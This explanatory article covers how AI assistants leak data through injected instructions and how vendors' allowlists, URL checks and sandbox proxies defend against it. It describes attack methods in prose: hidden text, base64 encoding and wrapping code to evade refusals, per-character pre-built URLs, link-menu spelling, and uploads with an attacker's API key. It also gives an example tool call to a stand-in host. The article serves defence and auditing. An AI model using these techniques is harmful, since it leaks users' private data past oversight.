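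The form trick worked again a few months later on Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, which by then also handled email. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* dates the report to April 21, 2026, and OpenAI has fixed the flaw. Earlier, in 2023, Google's chatbot Bard limited images to Google's own domains, but Willison's *Hacking Google Bard* explains that anyone could use Google's Apps Script service to run a small program on one of those domains and collect the data. Google said it had fixed that flaw. All three products allowed a Google-owned domain as if only Google could receive data there.

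### Antigravity: a request-logging site on the default list

Antigravity is Google's code editor, in which AI agents write and test software. The agents can control a browser, and an allowlist determines which sites it may open without asking. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* reported in November 2025 that the default list included `webhook.site`, a legitimate service that developers use to test whether their programs send requests correctly. Anyone can create an address there and see every request sent to it.

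PromptArmor hid an injected instruction in one-point type in an online programming guide, then asked the agent for help with the task the guide covered. The instruction told the agent to collect code snippets and the user's passwords for a cloud service, supposedly so that a tool could draw a diagram of the project. Antigravity's default settings stopped the agent from opening the password file with its normal file reader, so the agent printed the file with a terminal command, put the contents into a `webhook.site` address and had the browser open that address.

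Google's *Allowlist / Denylist* describes a further check, in which a server compares each site's name with a list of malicious sites and blocks any match, even if the user has allowed the site. This didn't help because `webhook.site` isn't malicious. It receives data for anyone who asks, which is harmless unless an agent with access to passwords can open it.

Human oversight was also weak. The recommended settings let the agent decide when to ask for a review, and users can leave several agents working in the background. The attack required the browser tool to be on, but PromptArmor found three other ways to get data out without it.

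PromptArmor didn't report the flaw before publication because Google already warned users about data exfiltration when they first opened the program. Google listed the problem among Antigravity's known issues, which earn researchers no reward, and said it was working on a fix. Agentpedia says `webhook.site` was still on the default list after the security company FireTail published another attack on Antigravity in March 2026 that sent source code to the same site. Agentpedia is a weak source for this, but an administrator can check the list.

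### Rovo: search switched off, but not the tool that opens pages

Atlassian makes Jira, which teams use to track tasks and support tickets, and Confluence, which they use to write shared documents. Its assistant, Rovo, works across both. An organization can turn off Rovo's web search, and an administrator might reasonably expect this to stop Rovo from reaching outside websites.

In August 2026, PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* showed that an organization's setting did not stop Rovo from leaking data. A user uploaded a guide that contained a hidden instruction and asked Rovo to organize some Jira tickets. Rovo added the contents of tickets and Confluence documents to a web address on the attacker's site and opened it. The setting had removed the search tool but left the separate tool for opening search results, which accepted any address. Anyone who returned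 to the chat later saw only suggestions for the tickets.

The attacker had no domain list to get around. The switch covered only one tool, and another could make the same kind of request, so it protected the organization less than its name suggested. An administrator can find such gaps by asking the assistant to open a page on a server the company controls, then checking that server's log.

PromptArmor calls the attack zero-click. The Hacker News (2026) objects that the victim still has to give Rovo the malicious content and make a request, although the leak itself needs no approval. The uploaded file is the least convincing part of the demonstration, but PromptArmor notes that an outsider could instead put the instruction in a support ticket, which a support desk is supposed to read.

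PromptArmor had reported the flaw on May 23. Atlassian assigned a case number but stopped replying, and Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published. Rovo also displays Markdown images from its answers, which could be a second way to leak data, but PromptArmor did not test this as a full attack.

Atlassian did fix another Rovo flaw that month. *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant* (Mascellino, 2026) describes RovoBlast, an attack by Varonis that, like Varonis's SearchLeak, began with a click on a prefilled link. Rovo's research agent, which can browse any website, then sent the data out. *One-Click Data Exfiltration via rovoChatPrompt URL Parameter (Confluence / Rovo)* (loacker) documents the same kind of flaw, for which Atlassian paid a $6,000 reward.

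### How to audit a domain list

An audit has to determine what a stranger could do with each domain on the list, even if a reputable company runs it.

The auditor first looks up who owns the domain, when its registration expires and whether anything still uses it. Somebody has to repeat this check regularly, because a domain's owner can change at any time. Unused entries should be removed. If Salesforce had still been using `my-salesforce-cms.com`, images hosted there would have stopped loading when the registration lapsed, and somebody would probably have noticed.

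Wildcard entries need particular care. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) gives the example of `*.amazonaws.com`, which a developer might add so that an agent can reach one storage folder on Amazon's cloud. Any other Amazon customer can create a folder that matches the same entry, so the list should contain the exact address of the folder the agent needs.

The auditor then checks whether the domain stores what it receives where outsiders can read it. Forms and request logs do, as do GitHub, where anyone can publish code, and npm, a public library of software packages. A service that accepts uploads into any customer's account is risky even if the accounts are private, because an attacker can supply the key to their own account, as happened with Anthropic's API domain. The risk depends on what the assistant can do. A browser loading an image can only send a GET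 request, which can't publish an npm package, but an agent that runs code can publish one.

The auditor also looks for redirects, especially pages that forward visitors to a destination included in the address. An output filter like Trusted URLs checks the address as written, so it approves a link to such a page on a trusted domain. Google has been testing a browser rule that also covers clicks, unlike a CSP on images. According to Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026), a site can list the addresses its page may contact, and the browser checks every connection the page starts, including redirects and navigation to another page, against that list. The trial was due to run from Chrome 148 to 151. Such a rule wouldn't have protected Superhuman, whose list included the domain that received the data, or Rovo, where the assistant's own tool opened the address.

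Finally, the auditor checks whether any service on the domain will fetch an outside address on request, as Bing and Teams did in the attacks on Copilot. A company can test its own services by submitting the address of a server it controls and watching for a visit. It can't test every feature of a large provider such as Google or Microsoft, and the provider may add new ones after the audit. Willison calls finding domains that nobody can use for exfiltration "a tricky proposition". For an assistant that handles customer records, it is safer to leave any large shared domain off the list unless the work depends on it.

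### What a strict list costs

A short list of trusted domains blocks some useful answers. TechNadu mentions agents that show pictures from outside sites, link to another company's documentation or send customers to a feedback form. Salesforce's rule blocks all of these until an administrator approves the domains. But one administrator found that Agentforce still redacted links to the company's own help articles after the relevant domains were on the list.

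Lists also take work to maintain. In the forum post *Browser Allow List not available*, a user of Google's Antigravity who has manually added hundreds of addresses asks for a way to add them in bulk. Antigravity offers an "always allow" button when the agent reaches a new site, which is convenient, but users then have to vet the site while trying to finish another task. When the code editor Cursor began asking for approval site by site, a user complained in *Web lookups now require authorization per site?* that this made the allowlist "pretty useless" and asked for a single switch to allow the whole web.

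Microsoft's *Control image rendering and embedded URLs* describes a Copilot Studio setting that blocks every image and clickable link in an agent's answers and shows a short notice in their place. Companies that use it have no domain list to audit for the chat window, but their employees can't click through to an answer's sources. That may be a small loss for a support desk that mostly needs order details and draft replies, though it would make a research assistant much less useful.

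Glean, which sells a workplace assistant, lets administrators judge links by their source as well as their domain. They can trust links that a tool returned to the model and have the software flag or remove other unapproved links, which the model may have made up. Employees can then follow links from search results without anyone approving each site in advance. The rule helps prevent exfiltration because an address written before the session cannot contain customer data that the model read during it.

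## ChatGPT: opening automatically only addresses that are already public

Under a rule OpenAI published in January 2026, ChatGPT opens an address automatically only if that exact address has already appeared on the public web, independently of any user's conversation. This means nobody has to decide which domains to trust. If the model writes an address containing a customer's phone number, that address should fail the test on any domain.

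### How the rule works

OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that explores the web by following links, much as a search engine does. According to OpenAI, the rule works as follows:

1. The crawler records the addresses of public pages. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. During a session, ChatGPT is about to load an address, for example to read an article or show an image.
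3. Software compares the whole address with the crawler's record.
4. If the record contains exactly the same address, ChatGPT loads it without asking.
5. If not, the software either tells the model to try a different website or shows the user a warning and waits for a decision.

Suppose the crawler has recorded `help.example/returns`, and an injected instruction gets the model to write `help.example/returns?name=Ana+Silva`. The domain and path are the same, but the full address is new, so ChatGPT doesn't load it automatically. An address that a user types into the chat is an exception. As far as Embrace The Red can tell, ChatGPT treats it as safe for the rest of that chat.

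OpenAI gives two reasons for not relying on a list of trusted sites. First, a trusted domain can redirect to an attacker's server. Second, people visit far more sites than any list contains, so a strict list would produce frequent false alarms.

The rule handles redirects better than a list does. A public address can still redirect ChatGPT to an attacker's site, but the redirect can't pass on private data if the original address contained none. The rule would also have blocked the Google Forms trick used against Superhuman, because no crawler could have recorded a form address containing the text of someone's emails.

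However, the rule can cause false alarms. The order page `help.example/orders/status?number=5512` is legitimate, but it concerns one customer and should not be in any public index. The software cannot distinguish it from an address that an attacker has filled with data. A support employee could therefore get warnings about pages the job requires, while someone reading the news would rarely see one.

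OpenAI promises only that ChatGPT will not quietly leak a user's data through the address. A page whose address passes the check can still contain false information or an injected instruction. OpenAI combines the rule with model training, monitoring and continual attack testing.

### The unexplained check of December 2023

Rehberger reported the image flaw to OpenAI in April 2023, when the company had no reward program for security reports and showed little interest in fixing it. He could still demonstrate the attack in December. The next day he noticed that ChatGPT's web page had begun checking each image address with an OpenAI server before displaying the image. The check used a function called `url_safe` and returned either safe or unsafe.

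OpenAI did not explain how the server checked whether an image address was safe. For Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, Rehberger tested 36 image addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit. Nine passed, including the one for "a" but not the one for "d", and he could see no reason for the difference. He could still send the word "hi" to his server as two images, one for each letter.

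The check also ran only if the app requested it. OpenAI had added the request to the web page but not to the iPhone app, which remained vulnerable to the original attack. Rehberger suggested moving the check to the server, which would protect every app. Willison (2023) called the fix "half-baked" and expected attackers to find ways of hiding data from it. Rehberger later found the check missing from the Mac app as well.

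Researchers gradually worked out that the server trusted certain domains. In October 2024, Rehberger reported two trusted domains where he could read server logs, `windows.net` and `apache.org`. Microsoft's cloud storage uses `windows.net`, and any customer can create a storage account there and see the requests it receives. The flaw was still unfixed when he returned to it in 2025. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* shows ChatGPT sending details of a user's past conversations to a storage account Rehberger had created. He asked OpenAI to publish the list of trusted domains and let companies configure it.

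In *HackedGPT* (2025), the security company Tenable found that `bing.com` always passed too. Bing's search results link to each site through a redirect on `bing.com`, so every site in Bing's index has a `bing.com` address. Tenable could not alter these links to add data, so it got Bing to index a separate page for each letter, then had ChatGPT display the matching links as images to spell out a secret.

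Tenable reported the flaw in December 2024, and OpenAI acknowledged the report the same day. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) lists six requests for an update from then until March, but no fix. Tenable's November 2025 account shows the attack working on GPT-5. These cases support OpenAI's later objection to lists of trusted sites, since a redirect had bypassed its own list.

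Around August 2025, OpenAI added further protections, which stopped the attacks Rehberger had published. The check also stopped being visible in the user's browser.

### ShadowLeak: a tool without the check

The 2023 check covered what ChatGPT displayed. Deep Research, a mode OpenAI launched in February 2025, also opens pages itself. It spends up to half an hour reading websites and any accounts the user has connected, such as Gmail, then writes a report. OpenAI's servers load the pages, so this is a server-side fetch.

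In *ShadowLeak*, the security company Radware tested whether an email could make Deep Research open an address containing private data. When the email simply asked for the data, the agent refused. When the email gave an excuse, the agent treated the address as suspicious and searched for it online instead of opening it. When the email named the browsing tool and blamed failures on a poor connection, some requests got through, but sometimes without the data.

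The attack became reliable once the email included an instruction to encode the data in base64, supposedly to keep it secure. According to Radware, this worked because the software sending the request received only a harmless-looking string. That is plausible, but Radware could not see OpenAI's software, and the results would be the same if the model had become more likely to send the data because the email presented the encoding as a protection.

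This research produced the restructuring email that OpenAI later reproduced. Radware reports that the attack succeeded every time in repeated tests, whereas OpenAI reports a 50% success rate for the same email and user request. Radware had several working versions, and the companies may have tested at different times, which could explain the difference.

The browsing tool was the layer that failed. Radware found no limit on the addresses the tool could open comparable to the limit on images. The user saw nothing, and the request never passed through the employer's firewall. Radware reported the flaw on June 18, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in early August.

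### ZombieAgent: addresses prepared in advance

OpenAI next stopped ChatGPT from adding anything to web addresses. The model could open an address only in the exact form it had received, so an instruction to put a customer's name at the end of one would fail.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* got around this restriction by preparing the addresses in advance. The attacker's email contained one address for each letter and digit, plus one for a space. ChatGPT found the secret in the user's mailbox and opened the matching addresses one after another. It never changed an address, so it complied with the restriction, which did not consider who had written the addresses.

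Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware also prepared a separate address for each character in each position. An "a" in the first position had a different address from an "a" in the second, so the attacker could put the characters back in order.

ZombieAgent could also continue after the first leak by using ChatGPT's memory, which carries information from one chat to the next. OpenAI had tried to keep this memory separate from connected accounts, but the block worked in only one direction, so ChatGPT could still read its memory first and a connected account afterwards. If a user uploaded a malicious file, the file could plant an instruction in memory to read the email the attacker had sent before every answer. Radware also showed that the attack could collect addresses from the victim's inbox, and the attacker's server would then send the same email to those addresses.

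Radware reported the flaw on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16. After the fix, ChatGPT opened a link from an email only if the link was in a public index or the user had supplied it, according to the January 2026 news article *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*. OpenAI published the general rule about six weeks after the fix.

The index makes the attacker do more work. In ZombieAgent, the attacker only had to write the addresses into an email. Now the attacker also has to publish the pages and wait for OpenAI's crawler to find them. Anthropic's rule for Claude, which depends on whether the model wrote the address, let data leak through links on fetched pages in July 2026. Willison says Anthropic has since fixed this.

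### How much can still leak

Even if ChatGPT can open only indexed pages, the model can still spell out a secret through the pages it chooses. Embrace The Red reports that OpenAI acknowledges this in its technical paper on the rule, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*.

An attacker with more pages needs fewer loads. If a secret has M possible values and the attacker has N pages, the model must make at least log M ÷ log N loads, rounded up. For example, a ten-digit customer number has 10 billion possible values. With 1,000 pages, each page can stand for a three-digit group, so the number takes four loads, the last carrying a single digit.

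| Public pages available | Digits sent per load | Loads for a ten-digit number |
|---|---|---|
| 10 | 1 | 10 |
| 100 | 2 | 5 |
| 1,000 | 3 | 4 |
| 100,000 | 5 | 2 |
| 10 billion | 10 | 1 |

The number of pages an attacker needs rises steeply as the number of loads falls. Going from ten loads to five takes ten times as many pages, and going from two to one takes 100,000 times as many. An attacker will therefore probably use a few hundred or a few thousand pages and several loads.

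The rule protects documents well because long texts are much harder to steal in this way. A 2,000-character email would take 2,000 loads with one page per character. Even with 1,000 pages, it would take more than 1,000 loads if the text used 36 equally common characters, though the model could shorten the text first. The rule protects short numbers poorly, since a six-digit login code needs only two loads with 1,000 pages.

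Rehberger's proposed limit on repeat visits could work by having ChatGPT store a copy of each page for a few minutes and reread that copy. He had not checked whether OpenAI already had such a limit. Tenable's tests in 2025 suggest that OpenAI had at least a partial one, because ChatGPT did not revisit a page it had already opened when answering questions about it.

The limit would work well against an attacker with only ten pages. The attacker would receive all of a ten-digit number only if its digits were all different, as they are in about one random number in 2,800. On average, the attacker would see six or seven different digits and would not know where the repeats belonged.

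But Radware's method of keeping characters in order also defeats the limit. The attacker publishes a separate page for each digit in each position, 100 pages in all, and the model never opens any of them twice. Sending the number in four loads takes 3,010 pages, with 1,000 for each of the three groups of three digits and ten for the last digit. If the requests arrive in order, 14 pages are enough in principle, because they can be opened in about 87 billion different orders, more than there are possible customer numbers. The limit takes little effort to add and is worth having, but it only makes the attacker publish more pages.

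Limiting the total number of loads would be more effective. In 2023, Rehberger suggested allowing one image per answer, or at most a handful. The limit would have to be very low, because with 1,000 pages each load can reveal three digits, and three loads would reveal nine of the ten. Such a limit is reasonable for images in a chat but not for Deep Research, which has to open many pages. OpenAI could instead look for suspicious patterns in its records of the check, such as a session that opens ten nearly identical pages on one small site.

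### What people do when they see a warning

When ChatGPT asks the user about an unverified address, it shows a dialog titled "Check this link is safe". The dialog explains that the link may share data from the conversation with another site, shows the address, and lets the user copy or open it. OpenAI advises users who notice something odd to avoid opening the link and ask ChatGPT for another source.

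OpenAI's posts give no figures on how often people open the link anyway, but research on other warnings is discouraging. *Revisiting the Design Agenda for Privacy Notices and Security Warnings* (2023) describes a study in which 53% of participants ignored warnings on a banking site and entered their passwords. In another study it covers, brain scans showed that people's brain responses to repeated security warnings weakened by the second showing and continued to fall with each repetition. The responses recovered after a period without warnings, which supports OpenAI's effort to keep them rare.

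People who use AI agents seem to behave similarly. In a survey of 16 users for *Options, Not Clicks* (2026), only three said they read permission requests carefully, and 13 used the "Always Allow" button just to make the requests go away. The sample is too small to give a reliable percentage.

In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) observed 303 people doing tasks such as choosing a job candidate or handling email with agents that an attacker had compromised. Only 8.6% noticed the attack. Warnings often increased people's trust in the agent, apparently by making it seem more transparent. The helpful warnings interrupted the work and were easy to check.

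ChatGPT's dialog interrupts the user, but the address can be hard to check. An employee may recognize a phone number in a web address but is unlikely to recognize one encoded in base64. Even a readable phone number doesn't prove that the link leaks data, because a legitimate order page may also have a customer's number in its address.

The content of the request matters too. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026), 80 volunteers approved or rejected actions proposed by an agent. Each volunteer used one of four kinds of approval screen and judged 12 actions, half of them harmful.

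| What the screen showed | Harmful actions approved | Harmless actions approved | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| Those details, the user's original instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
| The same facts, organized around the action's consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

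OpenAI's dialog most resembles the second screen, since it shows the address but not where the data in it came from. A better version for the support desk might explain that the address contains a phone number from a customer's record and that the link came from an outside email. The user would then have a reason to refuse without decoding anything. OpenAI's March 2026 account describes a dialog that goes some way towards this by showing the user the information about to be sent.

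The last screen may not be better than the log, because the adjusted estimate of the difference is compatible with no effect. Every other request the participants saw was also harmful, and an employee who has approved a hundred harmless links in a row would probably be less careful than they were. Even with the best screen, people approved almost a quarter of the harmful actions, so for customer records it is safer to refuse an unverified address than to ask about it.

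### Extending the check to other products

By March 2026, OpenAI called the check Safe Url and had extended it beyond ChatGPT's ordinary answers. According to OpenAI, it covers pages and bookmarks in Atlas, the company's web browser, as well as searches and page visits in Deep Research. Checking searches makes sense because a search query, like a web address, can contain private data.

Canvas, a workspace where ChatGPT can write and run small programs, uses a similar method, as do the apps that run inside ChatGPT. The programs run in a sandbox that detects unexpected attempts to contact anything outside it and asks the user for permission. The address check alone would miss these attempts, since a program can send data without ChatGPT opening a page, but the sandbox also leads to more permission requests.

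Every OpenAI team has to apply the check to its own product. Embrace The Red considers this the main remaining practical risk, because some developers may not know the protection exists. The iPhone app in 2023 and Deep Research in 2025 lacked protection that OpenAI had already built for the web page, and PromptArmor found that OpenAI's API log viewer displayed images insecurely.

### Lockdown Mode

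An organization can turn off many of the features that contact outside systems if it doesn't want to depend on the check or on its employees' judgement. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced an optional setting for this on February 13, first for large organizations, schools and healthcare providers. OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and smaller businesses on June 4. OpenAI recommends the setting for people who handle sensitive data and says most users don't need it.

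In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT reads only stored copies of web pages, and no live request leaves OpenAI's network. This prevents data from leaking through the choice of pages. An injected instruction can still make the model read ten pages in an order that encodes a customer number, but the attacker's server receives no requests. The drawback is that pages may be out of date or missing.

OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* lists the setting's other restrictions. Deep Research is off, and so is agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites. ChatGPT can't retrieve images from the web or download files for analysis, and users can't approve network access for programs in Canvas. Users can still upload files and generate images.

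Connected apps are harder to restrict because many companies need them. On personal and small-business accounts, Lockdown Mode stops ChatGPT from accessing outside services live or changing anything in an app if doing so would conflict with the mode's protections. In workspaces run by an administrator, Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically turn off every app, and the administrator chooses which apps and actions to allow.

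OpenAI advises these administrators not to enable apps they don't trust, even for reading. This is sensible because even a request to read something sends text to whoever runs the app. For trusted apps, OpenAI considers reading less risky than writing, and it advises against allowing a write action if an attacker might see the result. Under this advice, the mail-order company's assistant could look up an order but could not post a reply to the attacker's complaint, because the attacker could read the reply.

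A user on a personal or small-business account can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat, perhaps because a page is missing from the stored copies, and that chat may contain customer records. Lockdown Mode also has no effect on network access in Codex, the coding agent that leaked emails through a Google form in April 2026. Codex has its own network controls, including a domain allowlist, and OpenAI labels its internet access "Elevated Risk".

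Willison (2026) had criticized OpenAI's first check but thought Lockdown Mode looked "really good". It removes much of the outside communication that he had identified as the easiest part of the lethal trifecta to cut. It doesn't stop prompt injection, so a hidden instruction in an uploaded file can still make an answer wrong. OpenAI also warns that data could still leak through apps an administrator has enabled or through an unforeseen combination of features.

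## Claude: opening only addresses the model did not write

Anthropic's assistant, Claude, can open an address only if the whole address has already appeared in the conversation, for example in the user's question or in search results. The software refuses to load an address that Claude composed itself. OpenAI's check instead depends on whether the address is public.

Claude can also write and run programs, which can contact other servers without using the web tool. Anthropic restricts these programs to a list of permitted domains. Researchers have got data past both controls without breaking the rules the software enforced.

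### How the rule stops a composed address

Anthropic released the tool, called web fetch, in September 2025 for developers who build their own products on Claude. Their programs reach Claude through Anthropic's API, an interface for software instead of people. When Claude asks for a page, Anthropic's server loads it, so this is a server-side fetch. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for developers, Claude can open addresses that appear in:

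- user messages
- results from tools that run in the developer's own software, such as an order lookup
- results of earlier web searches and page fetches

Claude cannot open an address whose only source is Claude itself or a program it ran on Anthropic's servers. Otherwise, Claude could write a program that prints a new address, then open that address as though someone else had supplied it.

Suppose a complaint in the mail-order company's support queue contains an injected instruction to add the customer's name to `parcels.example/log?name=` and open the resulting address. Claude follows the instruction and calls the tool with `parcels.example/log?name=Ana+Silva`. The software looks for that address in the conversation, finds only the version without the name, and returns an error, so the attacker's server receives nothing. Writing the complete address into the complaint wouldn't help the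 attacker, who would have to know the name already.

As Willison (2026) points out, this blocks the basic attack deterministically, whatever an attacker has persuaded Claude to do.

The rule suits a support desk better than OpenAI's index does in one respect, because Claude can open a customer's order page if the company's order system returned its address. But a stranger who can get text into the conversation can also supply addresses for it to open.

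### Text that counts as the user's

In the API, the developer's program decides which text is labeled "user". Some programs put only the employee's typed question under that label. Others combine the question with the customer's email and record in one user message. Every address in the email then counts as the user's, although a stranger wrote it. The stranger could extract data with a list of prepared addresses, as Radware did in ZombieAgent.

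When the tool came out, Willison (2025) hoped that it would accept only addresses from users' prompts, but concluded that it "isn't quite that smart". Moving the customer's email out of the user message doesn't solve the problem, because the tool also accepts addresses from the results of the developer's own tools. The developer would have to remove the addresses from incoming emails before Claude reads them. This would probably work for a support desk, which rarely needs to open links that customers send.

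The developer also has to watch for tools that repeat their input. If Claude searches the order system for a web address and the "no order found" message repeats that address, the address is now in a tool result. Under the documented rule, Claude could then open it, even though Claude composed it.

Text that the employee actually entered can also be hostile. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal exercise from February 2026 in which a researcher emailed an employee a prompt ready to paste, in what looked like an ordinary request from a colleague. The employee gave the prompt to Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Among routine setup steps, the prompt contained instructions to read the employee's cloud credentials, encode them and send them to an outside address. Claude did all three in 24 of 25 runs.

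The exercise didn't involve the web fetch tool, but the tool's rule would allow addresses listed in such a prompt because the user supplied them. Anthropic explains that its defences in the model depend on what the user wants, so they had nothing to detect when the request came from the user. Only limits on the files Claude could read and the servers it could contact would have stopped the leak.

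### Options for restricting the tool further

Even with the provenance rule, Anthropic warns of exfiltration where Claude handles untrusted text alongside sensitive data, as a support assistant does. It advises developers to use web fetch only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. Developers who are concerned can turn the tool off, limit the number of fetches or restrict the domains it can access.

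The number of fetches is unlimited unless the developer sets `max_uses`. A low limit reduces how much can leak through Claude's choice of pages. According to Anthropic's August 2026 documentation, failed fetches also count towards the limit, so each wrong guess at an address uses up one fetch.

A request can specify either an allowlist or a list of banned domains, but not both. A ban does little to prevent exfiltration, since an attacker can register a new domain for a few dollars. An allowlist entry covers all subdomains, and a developer can narrow it to part of a site, such as `example.com/blog`. Anthropic also warns that lookalike characters, such as a Cyrillic "а" in place of a Latin one, can make two different domains look identical to the person checking the list.

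An allowlist containing only the mail-order company's own help site would complement the provenance rule well. The attacker would need an address that had already appeared in the conversation, on a site the company controls, and would still need a way to see the request.

### Paul's menu of links

Ayush Paul, a programmer, got around the rule in claude.ai, Anthropic's ordinary chat service, and published the method on July 9, 2026 in *The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026). He targeted Claude's memory. Every day, software condenses a user's recent conversations into a few paragraphs and adds them to each new chat. Claude can also search the full history. Even a new chat therefore contains private information, which Paul wanted to extract without relying on optional features or code execution.

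Paul first asked Claude to open a test-site address ending in the user's name. The rule blocked the request, as intended. Further tests showed that Claude could open addresses from the user's message, from search results and from links on pages it had already opened. Those links were useful to an attacker because a site's owner chooses what it links to.

Paul then built a site that worked like a keyboard. The first page had a link for each letter. If Claude opened the link for "a", the server created a page with links for "aa", "ab", "ac" and so on. Asked to spell the user's name this way, Claude opened ten pages, ending with one whose address ended in `ayush-paul`. Claude had written none of the addresses, so the rule allowed it to open them, even though its choice of links had spelled out the name. The rule did not take into account why Claude chose each link.

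Generating the pages on request also kept the letters in order, because Claude had to load one page before it could see the links to the next. Each page had a new address, so the leak would not have been stopped by using stored copies or by banning repeat visits to an address. The API's fetch tool refuses addresses longer than 250 characters, but an attacker could keep them short by storing the letters chosen so far on the server.

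Paul still had to get Claude to cooperate without the user asking it to. A few simple injections worked unreliably, and a story about a loyalty scheme made Claude suspicious. Paul succeeded with a coffee shop's website that showed what looked like a security check by Cloudflare, which protects many websites from unwanted automated traffic. On the page, Paul claimed that AI assistants could now identify themselves by giving their user's name, and presented the letter-by-letter links as a workaround for the limits of Claude's tool.

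The server showed this page only to visitors whose requests identified them as Claude. A person who opened the same address saw an ordinary coffee shop website, so checking the site in a browser would not have revealed this page.

Claude gave away the user's name, employer and hometown, while its answer in the chat looked harmless. Some of this information could help an attacker answer a user's security questions (Hackaday, *This Week In Security*, 2026). Paul used personal data for the demonstration, and there is no report of anyone attacking other users this way.

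Claude's resistance to the early versions fits Anthropic's test results. Anthropic reports that attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 in a Gray Swan benchmark succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt, and 5–6% of the time after 100 attempts that adapted to its responses. Paul needed only one story that worked, and could then have used it on every Claude user who asked about the site.

### Anthropic's fix and the API

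Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and paid him no reward. According to Willison, Anthropic had fixed the problem by July 15 by stopping Claude from opening links found on fetched pages. Claude could still open addresses that the user typed or that came from a web search.

This fix is stricter than a limit on the number of pages, and it makes Claude somewhat less convenient to use. If a user gives Claude the contents page of an online manual, Claude can no longer go from there to a chapter. The user has to paste the chapter's address, or Claude has to find the chapter by searching.

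Search results could in principle serve as another menu of links, much as Tenable used Bing's index to get data out of ChatGPT. This is more work than running one server that creates pages on request, and Paul did not test it.

The fix may not have reached developers who use the API. A copy of the API documentation from August 2026, a month after Paul's post, still lists earlier page fetches as a permitted source of addresses. Either Anthropic changed only its own chat service, or it had not yet updated the documentation. A developer can test this by putting a link to their own server on a page and asking Claude to follow it. Without that test, it is safer to assume that a product built on the API can still follow such links, and to set `allowed_domains`.

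### A file sent to someone else's Anthropic account

The provenance rule covers only the web fetch tool. A program that Claude writes can build any address it needs, so Anthropic has to control the program's network traffic separately. In claude.ai, programs run in an isolated container on Anthropic's servers. By default, they could contact only a short list of domains, mostly sites where programmers download software packages.

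Rehberger reviewed this list in October 2025 and focused on its first entry, `api.anthropic.com`. This is the domain of Anthropic's API, which includes a file storage service. Anyone with an Anthropic account can upload files there. The request must include an API key, a secret code that identifies the account, and the file goes to whichever account the key belongs to.

Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes how Rehberger stole a conversation through an approved domain. The user asked Claude to summarize a document that contained an injected instruction and the attacker's API key. Claude retrieved the user's last chat, saved it as a file and ran a program that used the key to upload the file to the attacker's account. The network control allowed the connection because the domain was approved.

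The upload limit was 30 megabytes per file. Sending that much text in web addresses of 250 characters each would take about 120,000 addresses. An attacker who can upload files can take the whole customer list instead of choosing which phone number to steal.

The attack worked on Rehberger's first try, but Claude then refused for a long time, apparently because an API key in a document looked suspicious. Encoding the key didn't reliably get past the refusals, but surrounding the suspicious code with harmless code did.

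Rehberger reported the flaw on October 25. Anthropic closed the report within an hour as out of scope, treating it as a model safety issue instead of a security flaw. On October 30 it confirmed that such flaws were in scope after all and blamed a mistake in its process. Anthropic's documentation at the time advised users to watch Claude and stop it if it accessed data unexpectedly. Rehberger proposed the firmer remedy of letting the container communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

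### Cowork: the same route from a user's computer

Anthropic launched Claude Cowork, an agent for general office work, in January 2026. It runs on the user's computer and can read and change files in a folder the user selects. Claude's programs run in a virtual machine, which isolates them from the rest of the computer and restricts their network traffic. The API domain was a permitted destination here too.

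Two days after the launch, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that Rehberger's route still worked. The user in the demonstration gave Cowork a folder of property documents, then uploaded a Word file that appeared to contain instructions for analysing them. The file also contained a hidden instruction, in tiny white letters, to upload the largest available document with the attacker's key. Claude uploaded a loan estimate containing financial figures and parts of social security numbers, and Cowork never asked the user for approval.

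This demonstration used Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models. PromptArmor also tested Claude Opus 4.5, which was better at resisting injections. Opus uploaded customer records to the attacker's account when given a malicious guide for connecting a new AI tool.

Anthropic acknowledged the risk and said it would update the virtual machine, according to TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection*. In its late May 2026 description of the fix, Anthropic admits that it had thought of the allowlist as a destination filter. It now regards each entry as a "capability grant", because allowing a domain allows everything a program can do there, and allowing the API had therefore allowed uploads to any Anthropic account.

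### Checking the account as well as the domain

Cowork needs the API to work, so Anthropic could not remove the API domain from the list. Instead, it added a proxy inside the virtual machine, a program that all traffic to the API has to pass through. When a session starts, the virtual machine receives a temporary token that identifies the session. The proxy forwards only API requests that carry this token.

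| Request from a program in Cowork | Domain check only | Domain and account check |
|---|---|---|
| To the attacker's own server | blocked | blocked |
| To Anthropic's API with the session's token | allowed | allowed |
| To Anthropic's API with the attacker's key | allowed | blocked |

A simple network filter can't make this distinction because web traffic is normally encrypted. It can identify the domain a program is contacting but can't read the key inside the request. Anthropic's proxy intercepts the request and reads it before passing it on.

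Anthropic also had a reason to put the proxy on the user's machine instead of its own servers. An upload with the attacker's key is a valid API request of a kind developers routinely make. The server can't detect that it came from someone else's Cowork session, but the virtual machine can identify its own token.

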